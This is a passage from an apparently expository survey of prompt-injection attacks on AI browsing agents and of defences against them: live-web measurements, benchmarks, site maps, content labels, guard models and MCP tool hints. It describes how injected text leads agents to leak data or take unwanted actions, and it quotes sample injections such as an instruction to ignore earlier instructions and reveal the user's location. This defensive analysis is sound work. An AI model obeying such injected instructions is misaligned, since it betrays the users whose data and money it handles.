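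Sending either message would most likely take a POST request, so a method filter would block both the resignation and the reply the user had asked for. The agent was supposed to ask for confirmation before sending anything, but this user was already expecting to approve an email. If the confirmation prompt showed only "Send this message?", a user in a hurry might well have approved it. If it showed the full text, the user could have noticed the mistake. The harmful prompt would have looked like the harmless one, unlike the prompts in the Comet attack, which would have been plainly out of place.

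### Injected instructions on the live web

All of these attacks were demonstrations. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang, 2026) looked for injected instructions already on the web by searching 1.2 billion addresses from an October 2025 crawl for nearly 4,000 phrases typical of prompt injection. After a review removed tutorials, news stories and other pages that only discuss such attacks, 12,075 injected instructions remained on 9,676 pages, or about one page in 124,000. Two other sources, which scan for servers connected to the internet, brought the total to 15,387.

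Very few of these instructions resemble the attacks on Operator and Comet. More than half were meant to disrupt the AI's output, for instance by telling it to return random numbers. Thousands more were written to keep AI systems from reusing a site's content or to expose bots posing as people. About 1,500 promoted a product, a source or a job candidate. Only 13 were meant to extract data, which was the model's own instructions in nine cases and secrets in the other four.

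Site owners placed most of the instructions themselves. In the main crawl, only 220 came from comments and other posts by visitors, although both the GitHub issue and the Reddit comment are of this type. The crawl includes few pages behind logins, little social media and no private email, the route used in the attack on Atlas. An attacker could also show the malicious text only to AI agents and serve crawlers an ordinary page. Khodayari and colleagues searched for known English phrases, so they would have missed the kind of polite office email that worked against Deep Research. Their count is therefore a minimum, and it is probably least complete for the most important attacks.

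Google ran a similar search and reached a similar conclusion. It found pranks, attempts to influence AI recommendations, and a few instructions to steal data or delete files, which mostly looked like experiments by individual site owners. Malicious examples rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026, but Google didn't publish the underlying counts, so the rise could have started from a very small number. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* reports that the security company Forcepoint also found no sophisticated, coordinated campaign, but that it saw the same templates on multiple domains and took this as a sign of organised tools.

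Khodayari and colleagues also tested whether the injected instructions they had found worked. They took 100 different ones, gave the pages containing them to 13 models in four formats, and asked for a summary each time. The models followed the injected instruction in 81 of 5,200 runs, or 1.6%.

| Format of the page | Injected instruction followed | Run ended in an error |
|---|---|---|
| Plain text | 3.9% | 0.7% |
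| HTML | 1.1% | 20.3% |
| Structured snapshot of the rendered page | 1.1% | 3.5% |
| Raw server response | 0.2% | 25.8% |

Plain text was the riskiest format because it removes the signs that an instruction was hidden from human readers. Fetch tools that return only a page's text have this drawback, though they are safer in most other ways. Small models did worst, following 8% of the instructions in plain text. The figures for HTML and raw responses are low partly because many of those runs failed on pages that were too long for the model.

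In six runs, the model warned about the injected instruction and followed it anyway, so a warning in an agent's report doesn't prove that the agent ignored the attack. The models in this experiment could only write summaries, so the results don't show how often a full browsing agent would have clicked, bought or sent anything.

### What WASP tests

WASP, a benchmark that Evtimov and colleagues published in 2025, tests agents that can act. It uses copies of Reddit and GitLab (a site where programmers share code). While working on an ordinary task, the agent comes across text that an attacker has posted. The attacker has only the powers of a normal user, who can write a post or an issue but can't alter the site. Because the sites are copies, researchers can let the agent finish a harmful action and then check whether it happened.

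This setup closely matches the first half of the Operator and Comet attacks, in which a stranger posted text on a reputable site. It is less like the second half, in which the agent did damage by carrying information to the wrong place. Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) note in *SPIDES* that each of WASP's ordinary tasks stays on one website and that its attackers are always users of that site. But agents often have good reasons to carry information between sites, for example to compare prices from several shops. WASP also leaves out attackers who run a whole website or place an advertisement on someone else's.

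An agent may have a low attack success rate on a test of this kind because it recognised the attack and refused, or because it started to obey and then failed to carry it out. Google observes that compromised AI systems often could not carry out malicious actions reliably in the past, and that today's systems are much more capable. A low rate for an old agent that could not complete attacks is therefore weak evidence that a new agent, which can work for hours, will resist them. A good benchmark should report separately how often the agent began to follow the attacker and how often it reached the attacker's goal.

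### Attackers who adapt

A benchmark usually has a fixed set of attacks, and real attackers can keep trying. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of k attempts succeeds is

1 − (1 − p)^k

If each attempt has a 1% chance of success, an attacker has about a 10% chance of succeeding at least once in ten attempts, and about a 63% chance in 100. The risk therefore depends on the number of attempts as well as the success rate. An attacker can make many attempts at once by posting the malicious text where many agents will read it. If 10,000 agents read the page and the attack works on 1% of them, about 100 users are affected.

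Treating attacks as independent is a simplification, and the real risk may be higher. Suppose a test contains 100 attacks, of which 99 never work and one always does. The average success rate is again 1%, but an attacker who can experiment will find the one that works and use only that, so users face a success rate of 100%. Experimenting is often cheap because the attacker can buy the same product and practise on their own account. Rehberger, for example, paid $200 for a month of Operator.

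A fixed set of attacks also quickly becomes less useful as a test. Once a developer has trained a model to resist a published set, the model scores better on that set even if it is no better at resisting new attacks. Zverev and colleagues write that defences which only make an attack less likely to succeed have repeatedly failed against attackers who adapt to them.

OpenAI responded to this problem by building an attacker that adapts. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (OpenAI, 2025) describes using reinforcement learning to find attacks on Atlas so that the company can fix the weaknesses before criminals exploit them. According to Fortune (2025), the attacking model tries an injection in a simulation, observes how the agent would respond, revises the text and tries again. It learned to steer the agent through harmful tasks of tens or even hundreds of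 steps. It also found strategies that neither OpenAI's human testers nor outside reports had identified, so a fixed test compiled from those human attacks would have missed them.

The same approach can improve a defence, as it did with the resignation message, but it reveals only the attacks that the attacking model can find. An outsider with a different model or more patience may find others. OpenAI reported in March 2026 that most attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because the model refuses. It also warned that separate filters for malicious text usually miss well-developed attacks, because detecting them is much like detecting a lie without knowing the context.

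Attackers can adapt to a method filter or a confirmation prompt, just as they can to a model. Rehberger noticed that Operator asked before submitting forms, so he built an attack that required only typing, with no form submission. If testers replayed old POST-based attacks against a new method filter, the attacks would all fail, but the testers would learn almost nothing about how well the filter stops an attacker who switches to GET.

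## Experiments with rules enforced outside the model

A method filter works the same way whatever the model outputs, which is its main advantage over training a model to resist attacks. Its weakness is that a request's HTTP method is weak evidence of what the request does. Since late 2025, several research groups have built prototypes that also run outside the model but use a fuller description of each step the agent takes.

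### What a click means

The effect of a click depends on what is under the cursor, which makes it hard to enforce rules on the agent's own commands, such as click, type and navigate. Meng and colleagues give the example of a rule that lets the agent click only at the screen position (246, 1023). That position may hold a link on one page and a delete button on another.

Blocking a whole command doesn't work well either. In an early trial, Meng and colleagues stopped an agent from navigating directly to Hacker News, the site from which Operator had leaked an email address. The agent could still search for the site on DuckDuckGo and click the result.

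The page's code is a better clue to what an element does than the element's position on the screen. *What It Is, Not What It Says* (2026) proposes working out what an element can do from its HTML and from ARIA, a set of labels that developers add mainly for screen readers. The method ignores the element's wording, so it treats a heading outside any link or button as only a heading, even if the text tells the agent to do something. Working out what an element does is still difficult, because developers can turn a plain block of text into a button, and a form may submit hidden fields that are missing from the version of the page the agent reads.

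*AC4A* (2026) instead uses a configuration file that links parts of a page to permissions. Before the agent sees the page, the software covers every part the agent lacks permission for. In a demonstration on a game's website, read permission made the game history visible, but the delete buttons stayed covered until the agent also had write permission.

### A site map for Amazon

CELLMATE, the system that Meng and colleagues published in December 2025, waits for the HTTP request that a click produces. To interpret the request, it needs an "agent sitemap", a list of the requests a website accepts and what each one does. Part of the one for Amazon looks like this, with asterisks standing for any text:

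| Request | What it does | Available rule |
|---|---|---|
| GET amazon.com/gp/cart/view.html* | views the cart | allow |
| POST amazon.com/cart* | updates the cart | allow |
| POST amazon.com/checkout/p/\*/spc/place-order\* | places the order | allow up to a spending limit |

With the site map, CELLMATE can let the agent change the cart while it blocks or limits orders, which a method filter can't do.

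The website's developers, or someone else the user trusts, write the available rules. When the user gives the agent a task, a language model picks the smallest set of rules that would let the agent complete it. This model receives only the user's request and the descriptions of the rules, so text on a web page can't influence its choice. The user then confirms the rules, and CELLMATE blocks requests to sites that the task doesn't involve. If the user doesn't name a site, as in "purchase a coffee maker", CELLMATE grants no permissions.

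Rules of this kind could have stopped Operator from buying eggs on Instacart. The reporter had asked it only to find the cheapest eggs, a task that doesn't require permission to place an order. CELLMATE applies its rules regardless of why an agent sends a request, so it can block mistakes as well as attacks.

### The 50-dollar limit

Suppose the user asks the agent to check out an Amazon cart if the total is under $50. CELLMATE enforces the limit in four steps:

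1. The model that picks the rules selects the one for placing orders and fills in 50 as the limit. The user confirms it.
2. On the checkout page, a script reads the total from the place given in the site map. Amazon's total appears on the page but not in the order request.
3. The script saves the latest total, because the browser has already closed the checkout page by the time it sends the order.
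4. When the agent clicks "Place order", CELLMATE recognises the request and compares the saved total with 50. It then allows or blocks the order.

The saved total can be wrong. If the agent raises the quantity and immediately places the order, the page may still show the old price, so CELLMATE slows the agent down to give the page time to update. The Amazon site map also finds the total by its position, as the fourth line of the order summary, so the script would read the wrong figure if Amazon added a line above it. Meng and colleagues recommend that developers give the total a permanent label in the page's code.

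Even with the right total, an agent could place two separate $49 orders, spending $98 while keeping each order within the limit. CELLMATE can prevent this by counting order requests and allowing only one. The same counter would stop an agent from ordering a second kettle after a time-out, but it would also block a legitimate retry if the first request never reached the shop.

The limit also depends on the model that picks the rules. Meng and colleagues tested three models on 209 tasks in retail, travel and software development. Each model picked exactly the right rules for more than 94% of the tasks in each category. The models did worse when they also had to fill in details such as a price limit or a quantity, getting both the rules and the details right on 81% to 97% of 32 retail tasks. In one error, the user wanted to put a sofa costing less than $300 on a wishlist, but the model gave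 the agent permission to add it to the shopping cart. The user is supposed to catch such errors when confirming the rules.

### Twelve scripted attacks

WASP's attacks were too weak to test CELLMATE properly. When Meng and colleagues repeated them without an added defence, fewer than 17% succeeded against each model they tried. They therefore assumed that the attacker already had full control of the agent, and wrote 12 scripts that carried out WASP's attacks on GitLab directly, for instance by deleting a project or adding the attacker's access key to the user's account. CELLMATE blocked all 12 attacks with rules that allowed only what the user's tasks required, which was to read an issue and to comment on it or upvote it.

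A plain method filter would probably have stopped nearly all of the attacks too, since most of them change something on GitLab. But it would also have blocked the user's comment and upvote, and CELLMATE's advantage in this test is that it allows useful actions like these.

The researchers tested CELLMATE on one website, for which they had written a site map of 51 functions by hand. Each attack required an action that the rules prohibited. If an injected instruction had told the agent to put private information in its comment, CELLMATE would have allowed it, because the rules permitted commenting. CELLMATE also can't interpret WebSocket traffic. A WebSocket is a connection that a page keeps open to exchange messages with the server, often for chat or shared documents, and sites use their own formats for those messages. Where a site map is incomplete or wrong, the user has only the protection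 that existed before CELLMATE.

The checks slow browsing slightly. A series of 11 steps on GitLab took 13.9 seconds without CELLMATE and between 7.25% and 15% longer with it, depending on the size of the site map. This delay is usually much shorter than the time an agent spends waiting for its model to choose the next step.

### Site maps compared with lists of permitted sites

In *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026) measured how much protection a site map adds to a list of permitted sites. Their system, COBRA, uses a modified version of CELLMATE's request checker, and the two projects share an author. Of WASP's 21 attacks, 19 required a request that the user's task didn't call for. With only a list of permitted sites, COBRA blocked the five attacks that led to another site, but the other 14 succeeded because they stayed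 on the site the user was already using. With site maps added, it blocked all 19.

In one of these attacks, the user wants to comment on a GitLab issue and the attacker wants to add an access key to a project. Both actions send a POST request to the same site, and only the rest of the address differs. The two attacks that COBRA could not cover depended on the wording of a comment that the user's task allowed.

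COBRA also has a model write the agent's whole plan before the agent opens any page. The plan might be to buy a kettle if it costs at most $50 and otherwise to report back. A second model reads the screen but can't add steps. This keeps injected instructions out of the plan, but a false price in a review could still lead the agent to buy when it shouldn't, which Zingrillo and colleagues call branch steering. To limit this, COBRA fixes in advance which sites, requests and values are acceptable in each part of the plan. In the researchers' own benchmark, branch steering succeeded 94% of the time against an ordinary agent and never against COBRA.

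Planning without seeing the pages makes the agent less capable. Claude Sonnet 5 completed 51% of 361 computer tasks as an ordinary agent but 39% under COBRA. Many of those tasks involved office programs instead of websites, so the loss on web tasks could be different.

COBRA also can't reliably enforce a spending limit if the total appears only on the screen, because the model that reads the screen might mistake a price in an advertisement for the shop's own. CELLMATE avoids this by reading the total from a fixed place in the page's code, but someone has to record that place and keep that record up to date.

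### How SPIDES tracks influence

If the user has allowed an order of up to $50, a malicious review could still persuade the agent to buy a different item for $45, and CELLMATE would let the order through. SPIDES, which Zverev and colleagues published in October 2026, addresses this by tracking which content has influenced the agent.

SPIDES relies on labels that websites add to their pages. Content counts as trusted if the site's operator can vouch for it, and as untrusted if it comes from someone else, such as a reviewer or advertiser. Private content also has a list of the sites that may receive it. The user decides which sites' labels to accept, and SPIDES treats everything on other sites as untrusted.

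On a shop's page, the agent would then see something like this invented example:

```
Electric kettle, $38
Latest review: [var_2]
Saved card: [var_3]
```

The agent can read the name and price, and it can pass the hidden items to a separate model that has no tools. The agent can also ask to see the review itself. SPIDES will show the review, but will treat the agent as influenced by untrusted content from then on.

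SPIDES applies two rules before each step. The agent may take a consequential action only if no untrusted content has influenced its decision or the data it is about to send, and it may send private data only to sites allowed to receive it. A step that only sends data, such as typing into a form without submitting it, needs to satisfy only one of these rules. An agent that no untrusted content has influenced may therefore type private data into any site. If a step breaks the rules, SPIDES asks the user to approve it.

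The first rule covers much more than purchases. On a trusted site, SPIDES treats every click, key press, form submission and visit to a new address as consequential. Zverev and colleagues assume that users have accounts only on sites they trust. Software can't easily detect whether a user is signed in, so SPIDES treats the user as possibly signed in to every trusted site.

SPIDES therefore doesn't rely on GET being safe on these sites. If an agent followed an injected instruction to open shop.example/account?do=close, a filter based on the request method would let the request through, but SPIDES would first prompt the user for approval, as it would before a click on "Place order".

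SPIDES treats opening an address on an untrusted site only as sending data. This makes sense if the user has no account there, but some sites accept changes from anyone. If the German wiki that OpenAI's agents edited was not on the list of trusted sites, SPIDES would have let them continue unless their edits contained private data, because the edits would otherwise have broken neither rule.

SPIDES also does little to prevent mistakes such as Operator's egg purchase. A shop would normally label its own listings as trusted, so SPIDES would have allowed the purchase without asking the user. CELLMATE's rules suit that case better.

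### The MicroNet test

Zverev and colleagues tested SPIDES on MicroNet, a set of 28 linked websites they built for the purpose. The sites have 470 pages in total and include a shop, a social network and a search engine. The test consists of 56 ordinary tasks, 22 of which require the agent to carry information from one site to another, and 56 attacks, half aimed at causing unwanted actions and half at leaking private data. The attacker may run a website, post on a trusted one or control an advertisement embedded in it.

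The researchers ran the tests five times with each of five models, including GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Opus 5.5. No attack succeeded against SPIDES with any model. Agents completed between 67.1% and 86.1% of the ordinary tasks, depending on the model.

In 50 of the 56 attacks, once the injected instruction reached the model, the test software replaced the model's output with the steps the attacker wanted, whether or not the instruction had fooled the model. This is a demanding test of the rules because it gives the attacker the result that a perfectly written injection would produce. In the other six attacks, the attacker supplied false data instead of an instruction, and the models chose their own steps.

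The test was much easier in another respect, because the researchers assumed a user who always judges approval requests correctly. SPIDES asked for an average of 1.84 approvals per completed task, and the assumed user approved every request during the ordinary tasks and refused any that the attacker had influenced. An attack that reached a confirmation prompt therefore counted as blocked, although a real user might have approved it.

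The researchers also labelled the sites themselves and treated their labels as correct. On a real site, a developer might forget to mark a review as untrusted, and SPIDES would then show the review to the agent as if the shop had written it.

### SOPGuard

A browsing agent can get around the same-origin policy, the browser rule that keeps one site's scripts from reading another site's content, by reading a page on one site and typing what it read into a page on another. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, June 2026) presents a benchmark for this problem and a defence called SOPGuard.

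In most of the SOPBench benchmark, the agent first handles private information on one site, such as a bank or an airline, then visits a page on another site that contains an injected instruction to reveal the information. The researchers combined ten types of private page with five types of public page, such as Reddit threads and Google Forms, and ran each combination three times in ChatGPT Atlas. Atlas leaked the data in 99 of the 150 runs, including 29 of the 30 with Google Forms, where the attacker controls the whole form.

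Data could also leak without an attacker. The researchers embedded a private page from one site in a page on another, and asked BrowserOS, an open-source browser with an agent, to summarise everything and type the summary into the outer page. It copied the private data every time, but didn't do so when it visited two ordinary pages one after the other.

SOPGuard records the origin of everything the agent reads. Before the agent types text into a page, SOPGuard checks whether any of that text came from a different origin and, if so, asks the user to approve the transfer. When Wang and colleagues added it to BrowserOS, the share of SOPBench runs with an unapproved transfer fell to zero. Tasks took 2.07% to 5.79% longer, and the agent completed about as many of them as before.

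Text is harder to trace to its source once the agent has summarised or combined it. SOPGuard relies on the agent's own model to report which sources it used, so the defence isn't fully outside the model. Of the three models tested, GPT-5.4 and OpenAI o3 agreed closely with human annotators, and the smaller GPT-5.4 mini agreed less. Wang and colleagues also tried injected instructions that told the model to misreport its sources. Hand-written versions hardly ever worked. Versions repeatedly revised by another model worked slightly more often but needed many more attempts. An attacker can reuse one that works, so the result of zero applies only to the original attacks.

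### Hiding untrusted content

*Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) sets stricter limits on what the agent may read. Untrusted content masking (UCM) replaces reviews, comments and similar content with labelled placeholders. The agent can ask a second model about a hidden item, but the answer must be a yes or no, a number, a date or a choice from a list that the agent supplies. An instruction such as "go to evil.com" doesn't fit any of these formats, so it can't reach the agent.

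On ten websites the researchers built, agents completed tasks about as well with UCM as without it, but the cost per task was 1.05 to 1.84 times as high. The researchers also rewrote WASP's attacks to make them stronger. These succeeded 17% of the time against an undefended agent and never against one with UCM. When the researchers deliberately marked one untrusted part of the page as trusted, the success rate against the agent with UCM rose to 6%.

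Some tasks can't be completed with such limited answers. If the user asks for the email address of a project's main contributor, the agent needs text from a hidden item. UCM can provide that text only after the user has checked and approved it.

An attacker can still make the second model give a false answer in the right format. Suppose the user asks the agent to invite Marko to a project called "dotfiles". The agent can't read the project names, so it asks the second model about each one, "Is this project name dotfiles?" If the attacker has given a project a name that tricks the second model into answering yes, the agent invites Marko to the wrong project. Nikolić and colleagues found this weakness themselves. They suggest checking all the candidates at once and treating more than one yes as a sign of tampering.

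### SPIDES, SOPGuard and UCM on the same test

Zverev and colleagues also ran SOPGuard and UCM on MicroNet. The ranges below cover the five models, and some figures combine results that the researchers reported separately for different kinds of attack or task.

| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 57.5–95.7% | 58.2–91.1% |
| SOPGuard | 53.2–73.2% | 58.2–93.2% |
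| UCM | 4.6–6.8% | 42.9–67.5% |
| SPIDES | 0% | 67.1–86.1% |

A competitor produced SOPGuard's figures on MicroNet, which includes many attacks SOPGuard wasn't designed to stop. SOPGuard checks text that moves between sites, but half of MicroNet's attacks aim at unwanted actions, and some of the leaks stay within one site. The poor result shows that SOPGuard covers too little to protect an agent by itself, but it doesn't contradict the result on SOPBench. There is less reason to suspect bias in the comparison with UCM, because Zverev also helped to create UCM. All of UCM's failures came from the six attacks with false data, which is the weakness its creators had described.

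The lowest completion rates also need careful reading, because safety filters run by the model's provider stopped Claude Opus 5.5 from completing some tasks that involved passwords or phishing messages. SPIDES hid some of this material from the model, so Opus 5.5 completed more tasks with SPIDES than without it. GPT-5.6 Sol better shows how much SPIDES usually lowers completion rates, since it completed 91.1% of the tasks without a defence and 86.1% with SPIDES.

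Two cases show why the boundary between sites is a poor guide to harm. In an ordinary task, the agent had to take a product's name from one site and look up its price on another. SOPGuard asked for approval in all 25 runs, 33 times in total, although the transfer was harmless. SPIDES didn't ask for approval in 21 of the runs. In an attack, a private message on a social network told the agent to copy the user's recovery email address into the user's public profile on the same network. SOPGuard didn't ask for approval, and the attack succeeded in all 25 runs.

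SPIDES blocked that attack every time. Its rules would allow the agent to type the address into the profile, because the data stays on the same site, but they require approval to click "Save changes". Zverev and colleagues assume that typing has no lasting effect until someone submits the form. The web apps Rehberger mentioned save text as the user types, so SPIDES would have no click to block.

SOPGuard required 0.22 approvals per completed task, compared with 1.84 for SPIDES. Much of that difference comes from attacks and actions that SOPGuard isn't designed to control. When the researchers added enough approvals to give all the defences the same protection, SPIDES generally completed the most tasks with few approvals.

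### What websites would have to supply

SOPGuard needs nothing from websites, because a browser can always identify a page's origin. CELLMATE and COBRA can restrict an agent to certain sites on their own, but they need a site map to control what the agent does on those sites. UCM needs labels for untrusted content. SPIDES needs those labels, plus labels for private content and for the sites that may receive it.

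Nikolić and colleagues needed only 15 to 30 rules per site to mark all the untrusted content on GitLab, Reddit and Booking.com. A site map takes more work, and developers have to update it whenever they add or change a function.

Software can do part of the mapping and labeling. Zingrillo and colleagues built a crawler that drafts site maps, and its drafts contained every function needed for 18 of 25 tasks on one benchmark and 18 of 26 on another. Nikolić and colleagues had a model label pages from their structure alone, removing the text because it could contain an attack. The model missed none of the types of untrusted content on Reddit but missed 5.8% on Booking.com and 8.5% on GitLab. An attacker can use a gap in the labels, so a person would still have to check them.

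Meng and colleagues expect websites to cooperate to protect their users and attract more of them. Developers already publish similar information, such as rules for crawlers and lists of the scripts a browser may run. Nikolić and colleagues add that OpenAI asks site owners for ARIA labels to help Atlas use their pages. Site owners have less to gain directly from security labels, however, because these mostly restrict the agent rather than help it use the site.

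Zingrillo and colleagues are less confident, because some sites earn money from advertising to human visitors and others may not want to give agents a list of everything the site can do. A site could also label its content dishonestly. If a shop marked a paid advertisement as trusted, SPIDES would show it to the agent, and the user's only remedy would be to stop trusting the shop.

For years, many sites ignored the much simpler rule that GET requests should be safe, which gives some reason to doubt that they would provide site maps or labels. Meng and colleagues argue against relying on sites to offer special tools for agents, because most websites took about two decades to adopt encryption. The site maps they propose could face the same delay, though outside pressure might shorten it. Senders of marketing email had a strong reason to support one-click unsubscribing by POST once Gmail and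 Yahoo expected it, and the companies that make browsers and agents could ask for site maps or labels in the same way.

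## Predicting which clicks and requests have consequences

Most websites don't give agents a site map like CELLMATE's or page labels like those SPIDES relies on. Without them, a second model can look at the page and predict what a click will do. Alternatively, developers can give an agent ready-made tools, such as "search products" or "place order", and label each one by its effects.

### How WebGuard rates a click

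For *WebGuard*, Zheng, Liao and colleagues (2025) collected 4,939 actions on 193 websites, including shops, government services and 15 little-visited sites. Trained annotators rated the risk of each action, usually a click on one element of a page.

| Rating | Meaning | Examples |
|---|---|---|
| SAFE | Trivial effects that the user can undo at once | Following a link, using the search bar, typing a review without submitting it |
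| LOW | Minor, reversible effects on the user alone | Logging out, changing the language, adding an item to a cart |
| HIGH | Serious or irreversible effects, which may involve other people, money or the law | Posting a review, booking a test drive, deleting an account, sending an email |

Each annotator spent up to an hour on a website looking for every action that changed something. They filled in any form that a button required, then recorded and rated the action. To avoid harm, they pressed a risky button only if they couldn't otherwise tell what it did, and they could correct its rating afterwards. Everything else on the page counted as SAFE by default. Three reviewers checked the results.

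The final counts were 1,108 HIGH, 2,284 LOW and 1,564 SAFE actions, which add up to slightly more than the stated total. About 22% of the actions were HIGH. That share is probably far higher than in ordinary browsing, because the annotators looked for such actions.

### How the models of 2025 scored

Zheng and colleagues gave each model the definitions, the proposed action and the page, as a screenshot or a text outline. They measured accuracy (the share of all actions the model rated correctly) and recall on HIGH actions (the share of HIGH actions it rated HIGH). Without further training, no model reached an average accuracy of 60% across four test sets. GPT-4o, Claude 3.7 Sonnet and o3, among the leading models of the time, identified fewer than 60% of the HIGH actions in each test set.

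The researchers then fine-tuned Qwen2.5-VL-7B, a small open model, on 1,982 of the labelled actions. Its accuracy rose from 37% to 80%, and its recall on HIGH actions from 20% to 76%. It recognised 90.2% of HIGH actions on new sites from familiar categories, but only 66.8% on social and entertainment sites, which the training data left out entirely.

Those unfamiliar categories made up the largest test set, with 1,669 actions. These are the results for models that worked from screenshots:

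| Model | Accuracy | Recall on HIGH | Recall on LOW |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-VL-7B | 38.3% | 22.3% | 18.5% |
| The same model after fine-tuning | 75.2% | 66.8% | 87.5% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 55.9% | 38.1% | 67.7% |
| GPT-4o | 60.6% | 39.0% | 89.2% |
| o3 | 62.0% | 38.7% | 87.8% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 45.9% | 66.3% | 21.3% |

GPT-4o-mini was much less accurate than o3 but recognised far more of the HIGH actions, about as many as the fine-tuned model. It probably recognised so many partly because it rated minor actions as serious, which would also explain its low recall on LOW actions.

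### Why recall matters more than accuracy

Suppose an agent makes 1,000 clicks, ten of which would do something serious, such as placing an order. A guard model that rates every click as harmless is 99% accurate but stops none of the ten. A model that flags nine of the serious clicks and 50 harmless ones is only 94.9% accurate, but it could prevent up to nine accidents.

The second model's user has to answer 59 warnings, 50 of them needless. A guard model could reach perfect recall by warning about every click, so recall means little without the number of false alarms.

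Zheng and colleagues want recall close to 100%, because even 95% would let one in 20 risky actions through. Their fine-tuned model falls well short. They also found that models overestimated the risk of harmless steps within serious tasks. One model rated a "Checkout" button HIGH, although it only opened the next page. Another error involved a checkbox in a US passport application, although ticking it committed the applicant to nothing.

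None of these tests involved an attacker. A guard model that reads the page also reads any text strangers have posted there, so a review claiming that "Place order" only shows a preview might mislead both the guard and the agent.

### WebGuard's ratings and HTTP methods

The WebGuard annotation tool saved screenshots, the positions of elements and details from the page's code. Zheng and colleagues don't mention saving HTTP requests, so the published data can't show how often a method filter would agree with the ratings. This comparison relies on how websites usually work:

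| Action | Rating | Usual request | Possible exception |
|---|---|---|---|
| Typing a review without submitting it | SAFE | None | POST, if the page saves drafts |
| Using the search bar | SAFE | GET | POST, as in the manufacturer's catalogue that Jacobs describes |
| Changing the language | LOW | GET or POST | |
| Logging out | LOW | GET or POST | |
| Adding an item to a cart | LOW | POST | GET, if the shop uses a plain link |
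| Sending an email | HIGH | POST | A message over a WebSocket |
| Deleting an account | HIGH | POST | GET, if the site breaks the HTTP rule |

The ratings distinguish a cart update from an order, which a method filter does not. The request method can still help when a button's wording is misleading. For example, if the "Checkout" button sent a GET request, a method filter would have allowed it without a warning.

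Neither the ratings nor the methods handle data leaks well. WebGuard lists following a link as an example of a SAFE action, even though the link's address may contain the user's private data. It also lists typing without submitting, but Rehberger's attack on Operator needed only typing.

The ratings also don't account for what the user wants, because the models had instructions to judge each action by itself. "Place order" is rated HIGH whether the user asked for a purchase or only for a price. In a demonstration by Zheng and colleagues, the guard model rates a "Sign up" button on Avvo, a legal-services site, HIGH because opening an account may mean accepting legal terms. The user can then approve, reject or change the step.

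### Guard models since WebGuard

No one appears to have published a rerun of WebGuard with 2026 models, which are much more capable than o3, so its scores are a poor guide to how current models would do. Newer projects have mostly changed the task.

In *OSGuard* (2026), the guard model also receives the user's instruction and rates each proposed action as allowed, unrelated or unsafe. If it blocks an action, it gives the agent a reason, and the agent can make up to two more proposals. Such a guard might have classed Operator's egg purchase as unrelated.

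Other projects look beyond the next step. *SafePred* (2026) distinguishes predicting the next page from judging whether the result is safe, and proposes predicting long-term risks as well. The guard in *DreamGuard* (2026) scores both the proposed action and the risk accumulated over earlier steps. It can allow the action, block it, or hold it when the evidence is uncertain.

It also matters who decides when to use the predictor. *Predictive Safety Guardrails Do Not Always Make LLM Agents Safer* (2026) distinguishes between letting the agent choose whether to consult a predictor and having a guard check actions before they run. In the first design, the agent can skip the check or ignore the result. The OpenAI model that spent someone else's test tokens might well have done so.

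### Hints in the Model Context Protocol

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting language models to outside tools. A server offers tools, such as one that deletes a file, and a host program runs the model and passes its calls to the server. Since March 2025, a server has been able to attach four yes-or-no hints to each tool. The project's blog, Model Context Protocol (2026), explains them and the defaults for tools without hints:

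| Hint | What it states | Default |
|---|---|---|
| readOnlyHint | The tool changes nothing | No |
| destructiveHint | Any changes may be destructive, as opposed to only adding something | Yes |
| idempotentHint | Repeating the same call is safe | No |
| openWorldHint | The tool deals with outside systems or people | Yes |

A host can use the hints to decide when to ask the user for approval. The HTTP method would be little help, because a search is sent as a POST in an example that Model Context Protocol (2026) gives for the July 2026 revision. The new headers include the tool's name, so a filter could instead check that name against a list of permitted tools.

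An action can be consequential without being destructive. In StackOne's scheme for setting the hints, creating a support ticket is non-destructive and deleting an issue is destructive. By the same logic, sending an email or placing an order only adds something, so an honest developer could mark either tool as non-destructive. A host that asked for approval only before using destructive tools would then let the agent spend the user's money without approval.

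Codex CLI, the terminal version of OpenAI's programming agent, uses a better rule. *When Neither Side Confirms* (Yao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) reports that Codex CLI asks for approval unless a tool is marked as non-destructive and as either read-only or confined to a closed system. A tool that places orders with an outside shop would therefore need approval if it were labelled accurately.

The hint about repetition also provides no idempotency key and no way to check whether an earlier call succeeded, as Trofimov and Novikov (2026) point out in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*. They also describe a failure that accurate hints on both tools involved would not have prevented. An agent with a budget of €1,500 books a €900 flight and a €700 hotel at the same time. Each booking is within the budget, but together they exceed it, so the agent cancels the hotel and is left with a non-refundable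 flight.

### Trusting a label from an unknown server

The MCP specification requires host programs to treat hints as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. During the protocol's review of hints, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of its creators, asked how a program could use a hint that it couldn't trust. Another participant, Basil Hosmer, wanted programs to ignore hints from untrusted servers, but the specification lets each host decide how much weight to give them. In practice, most hosts trust a server if the user chose to install it, according to Model Context Protocol.

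According to the project's blog, a server can mark a tool as read-only and still delete the user's files. The blog recommends network controls or an isolated environment when a user needs a guarantee.

### Labels in WebMCP

WebMCP is a proposal to let websites offer similar tools directly to an agent in the browser. A shop could provide a "place order" function in JavaScript, so the agent wouldn't have to find and click the right button. The Web Machine Learning Community Group's *WebMCP* is a draft with editors from Microsoft and Google. It is not a W3C standard or on the way to becoming one. According to minutes from W3C (2026), architecture, privacy and security reviews were under way in August.

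Two of its labels are readOnlyHint, which MCP also has, and untrustedContentHint, which marks tools whose output may contain text from strangers. Search Engine Journal gives the example of a tool that shows product reviews, which should have both labels because it only reads data and anyone can write a review. According to the article, web and marketing staff will probably add many of these labels without much help from security specialists.

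Google advises agent developers to classify all data returned through WebMCP as "strictly untrusted" (Chrome for Developers, 2026), which is stricter than the labels. The text that describes a tool can also contain an attack. *Privacy and security considerations for WebMCP* (Huang, 2025) gives the example of a weather tool whose name includes an instruction to ignore earlier instructions and provide the user's location. A yes-or-no label cannot contain such an instruction, but it can be false, and a false read-only label could do particular damage because, as Huang notes, agents can act with the user's identity in the browser.

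### How often labels are missing or wrong

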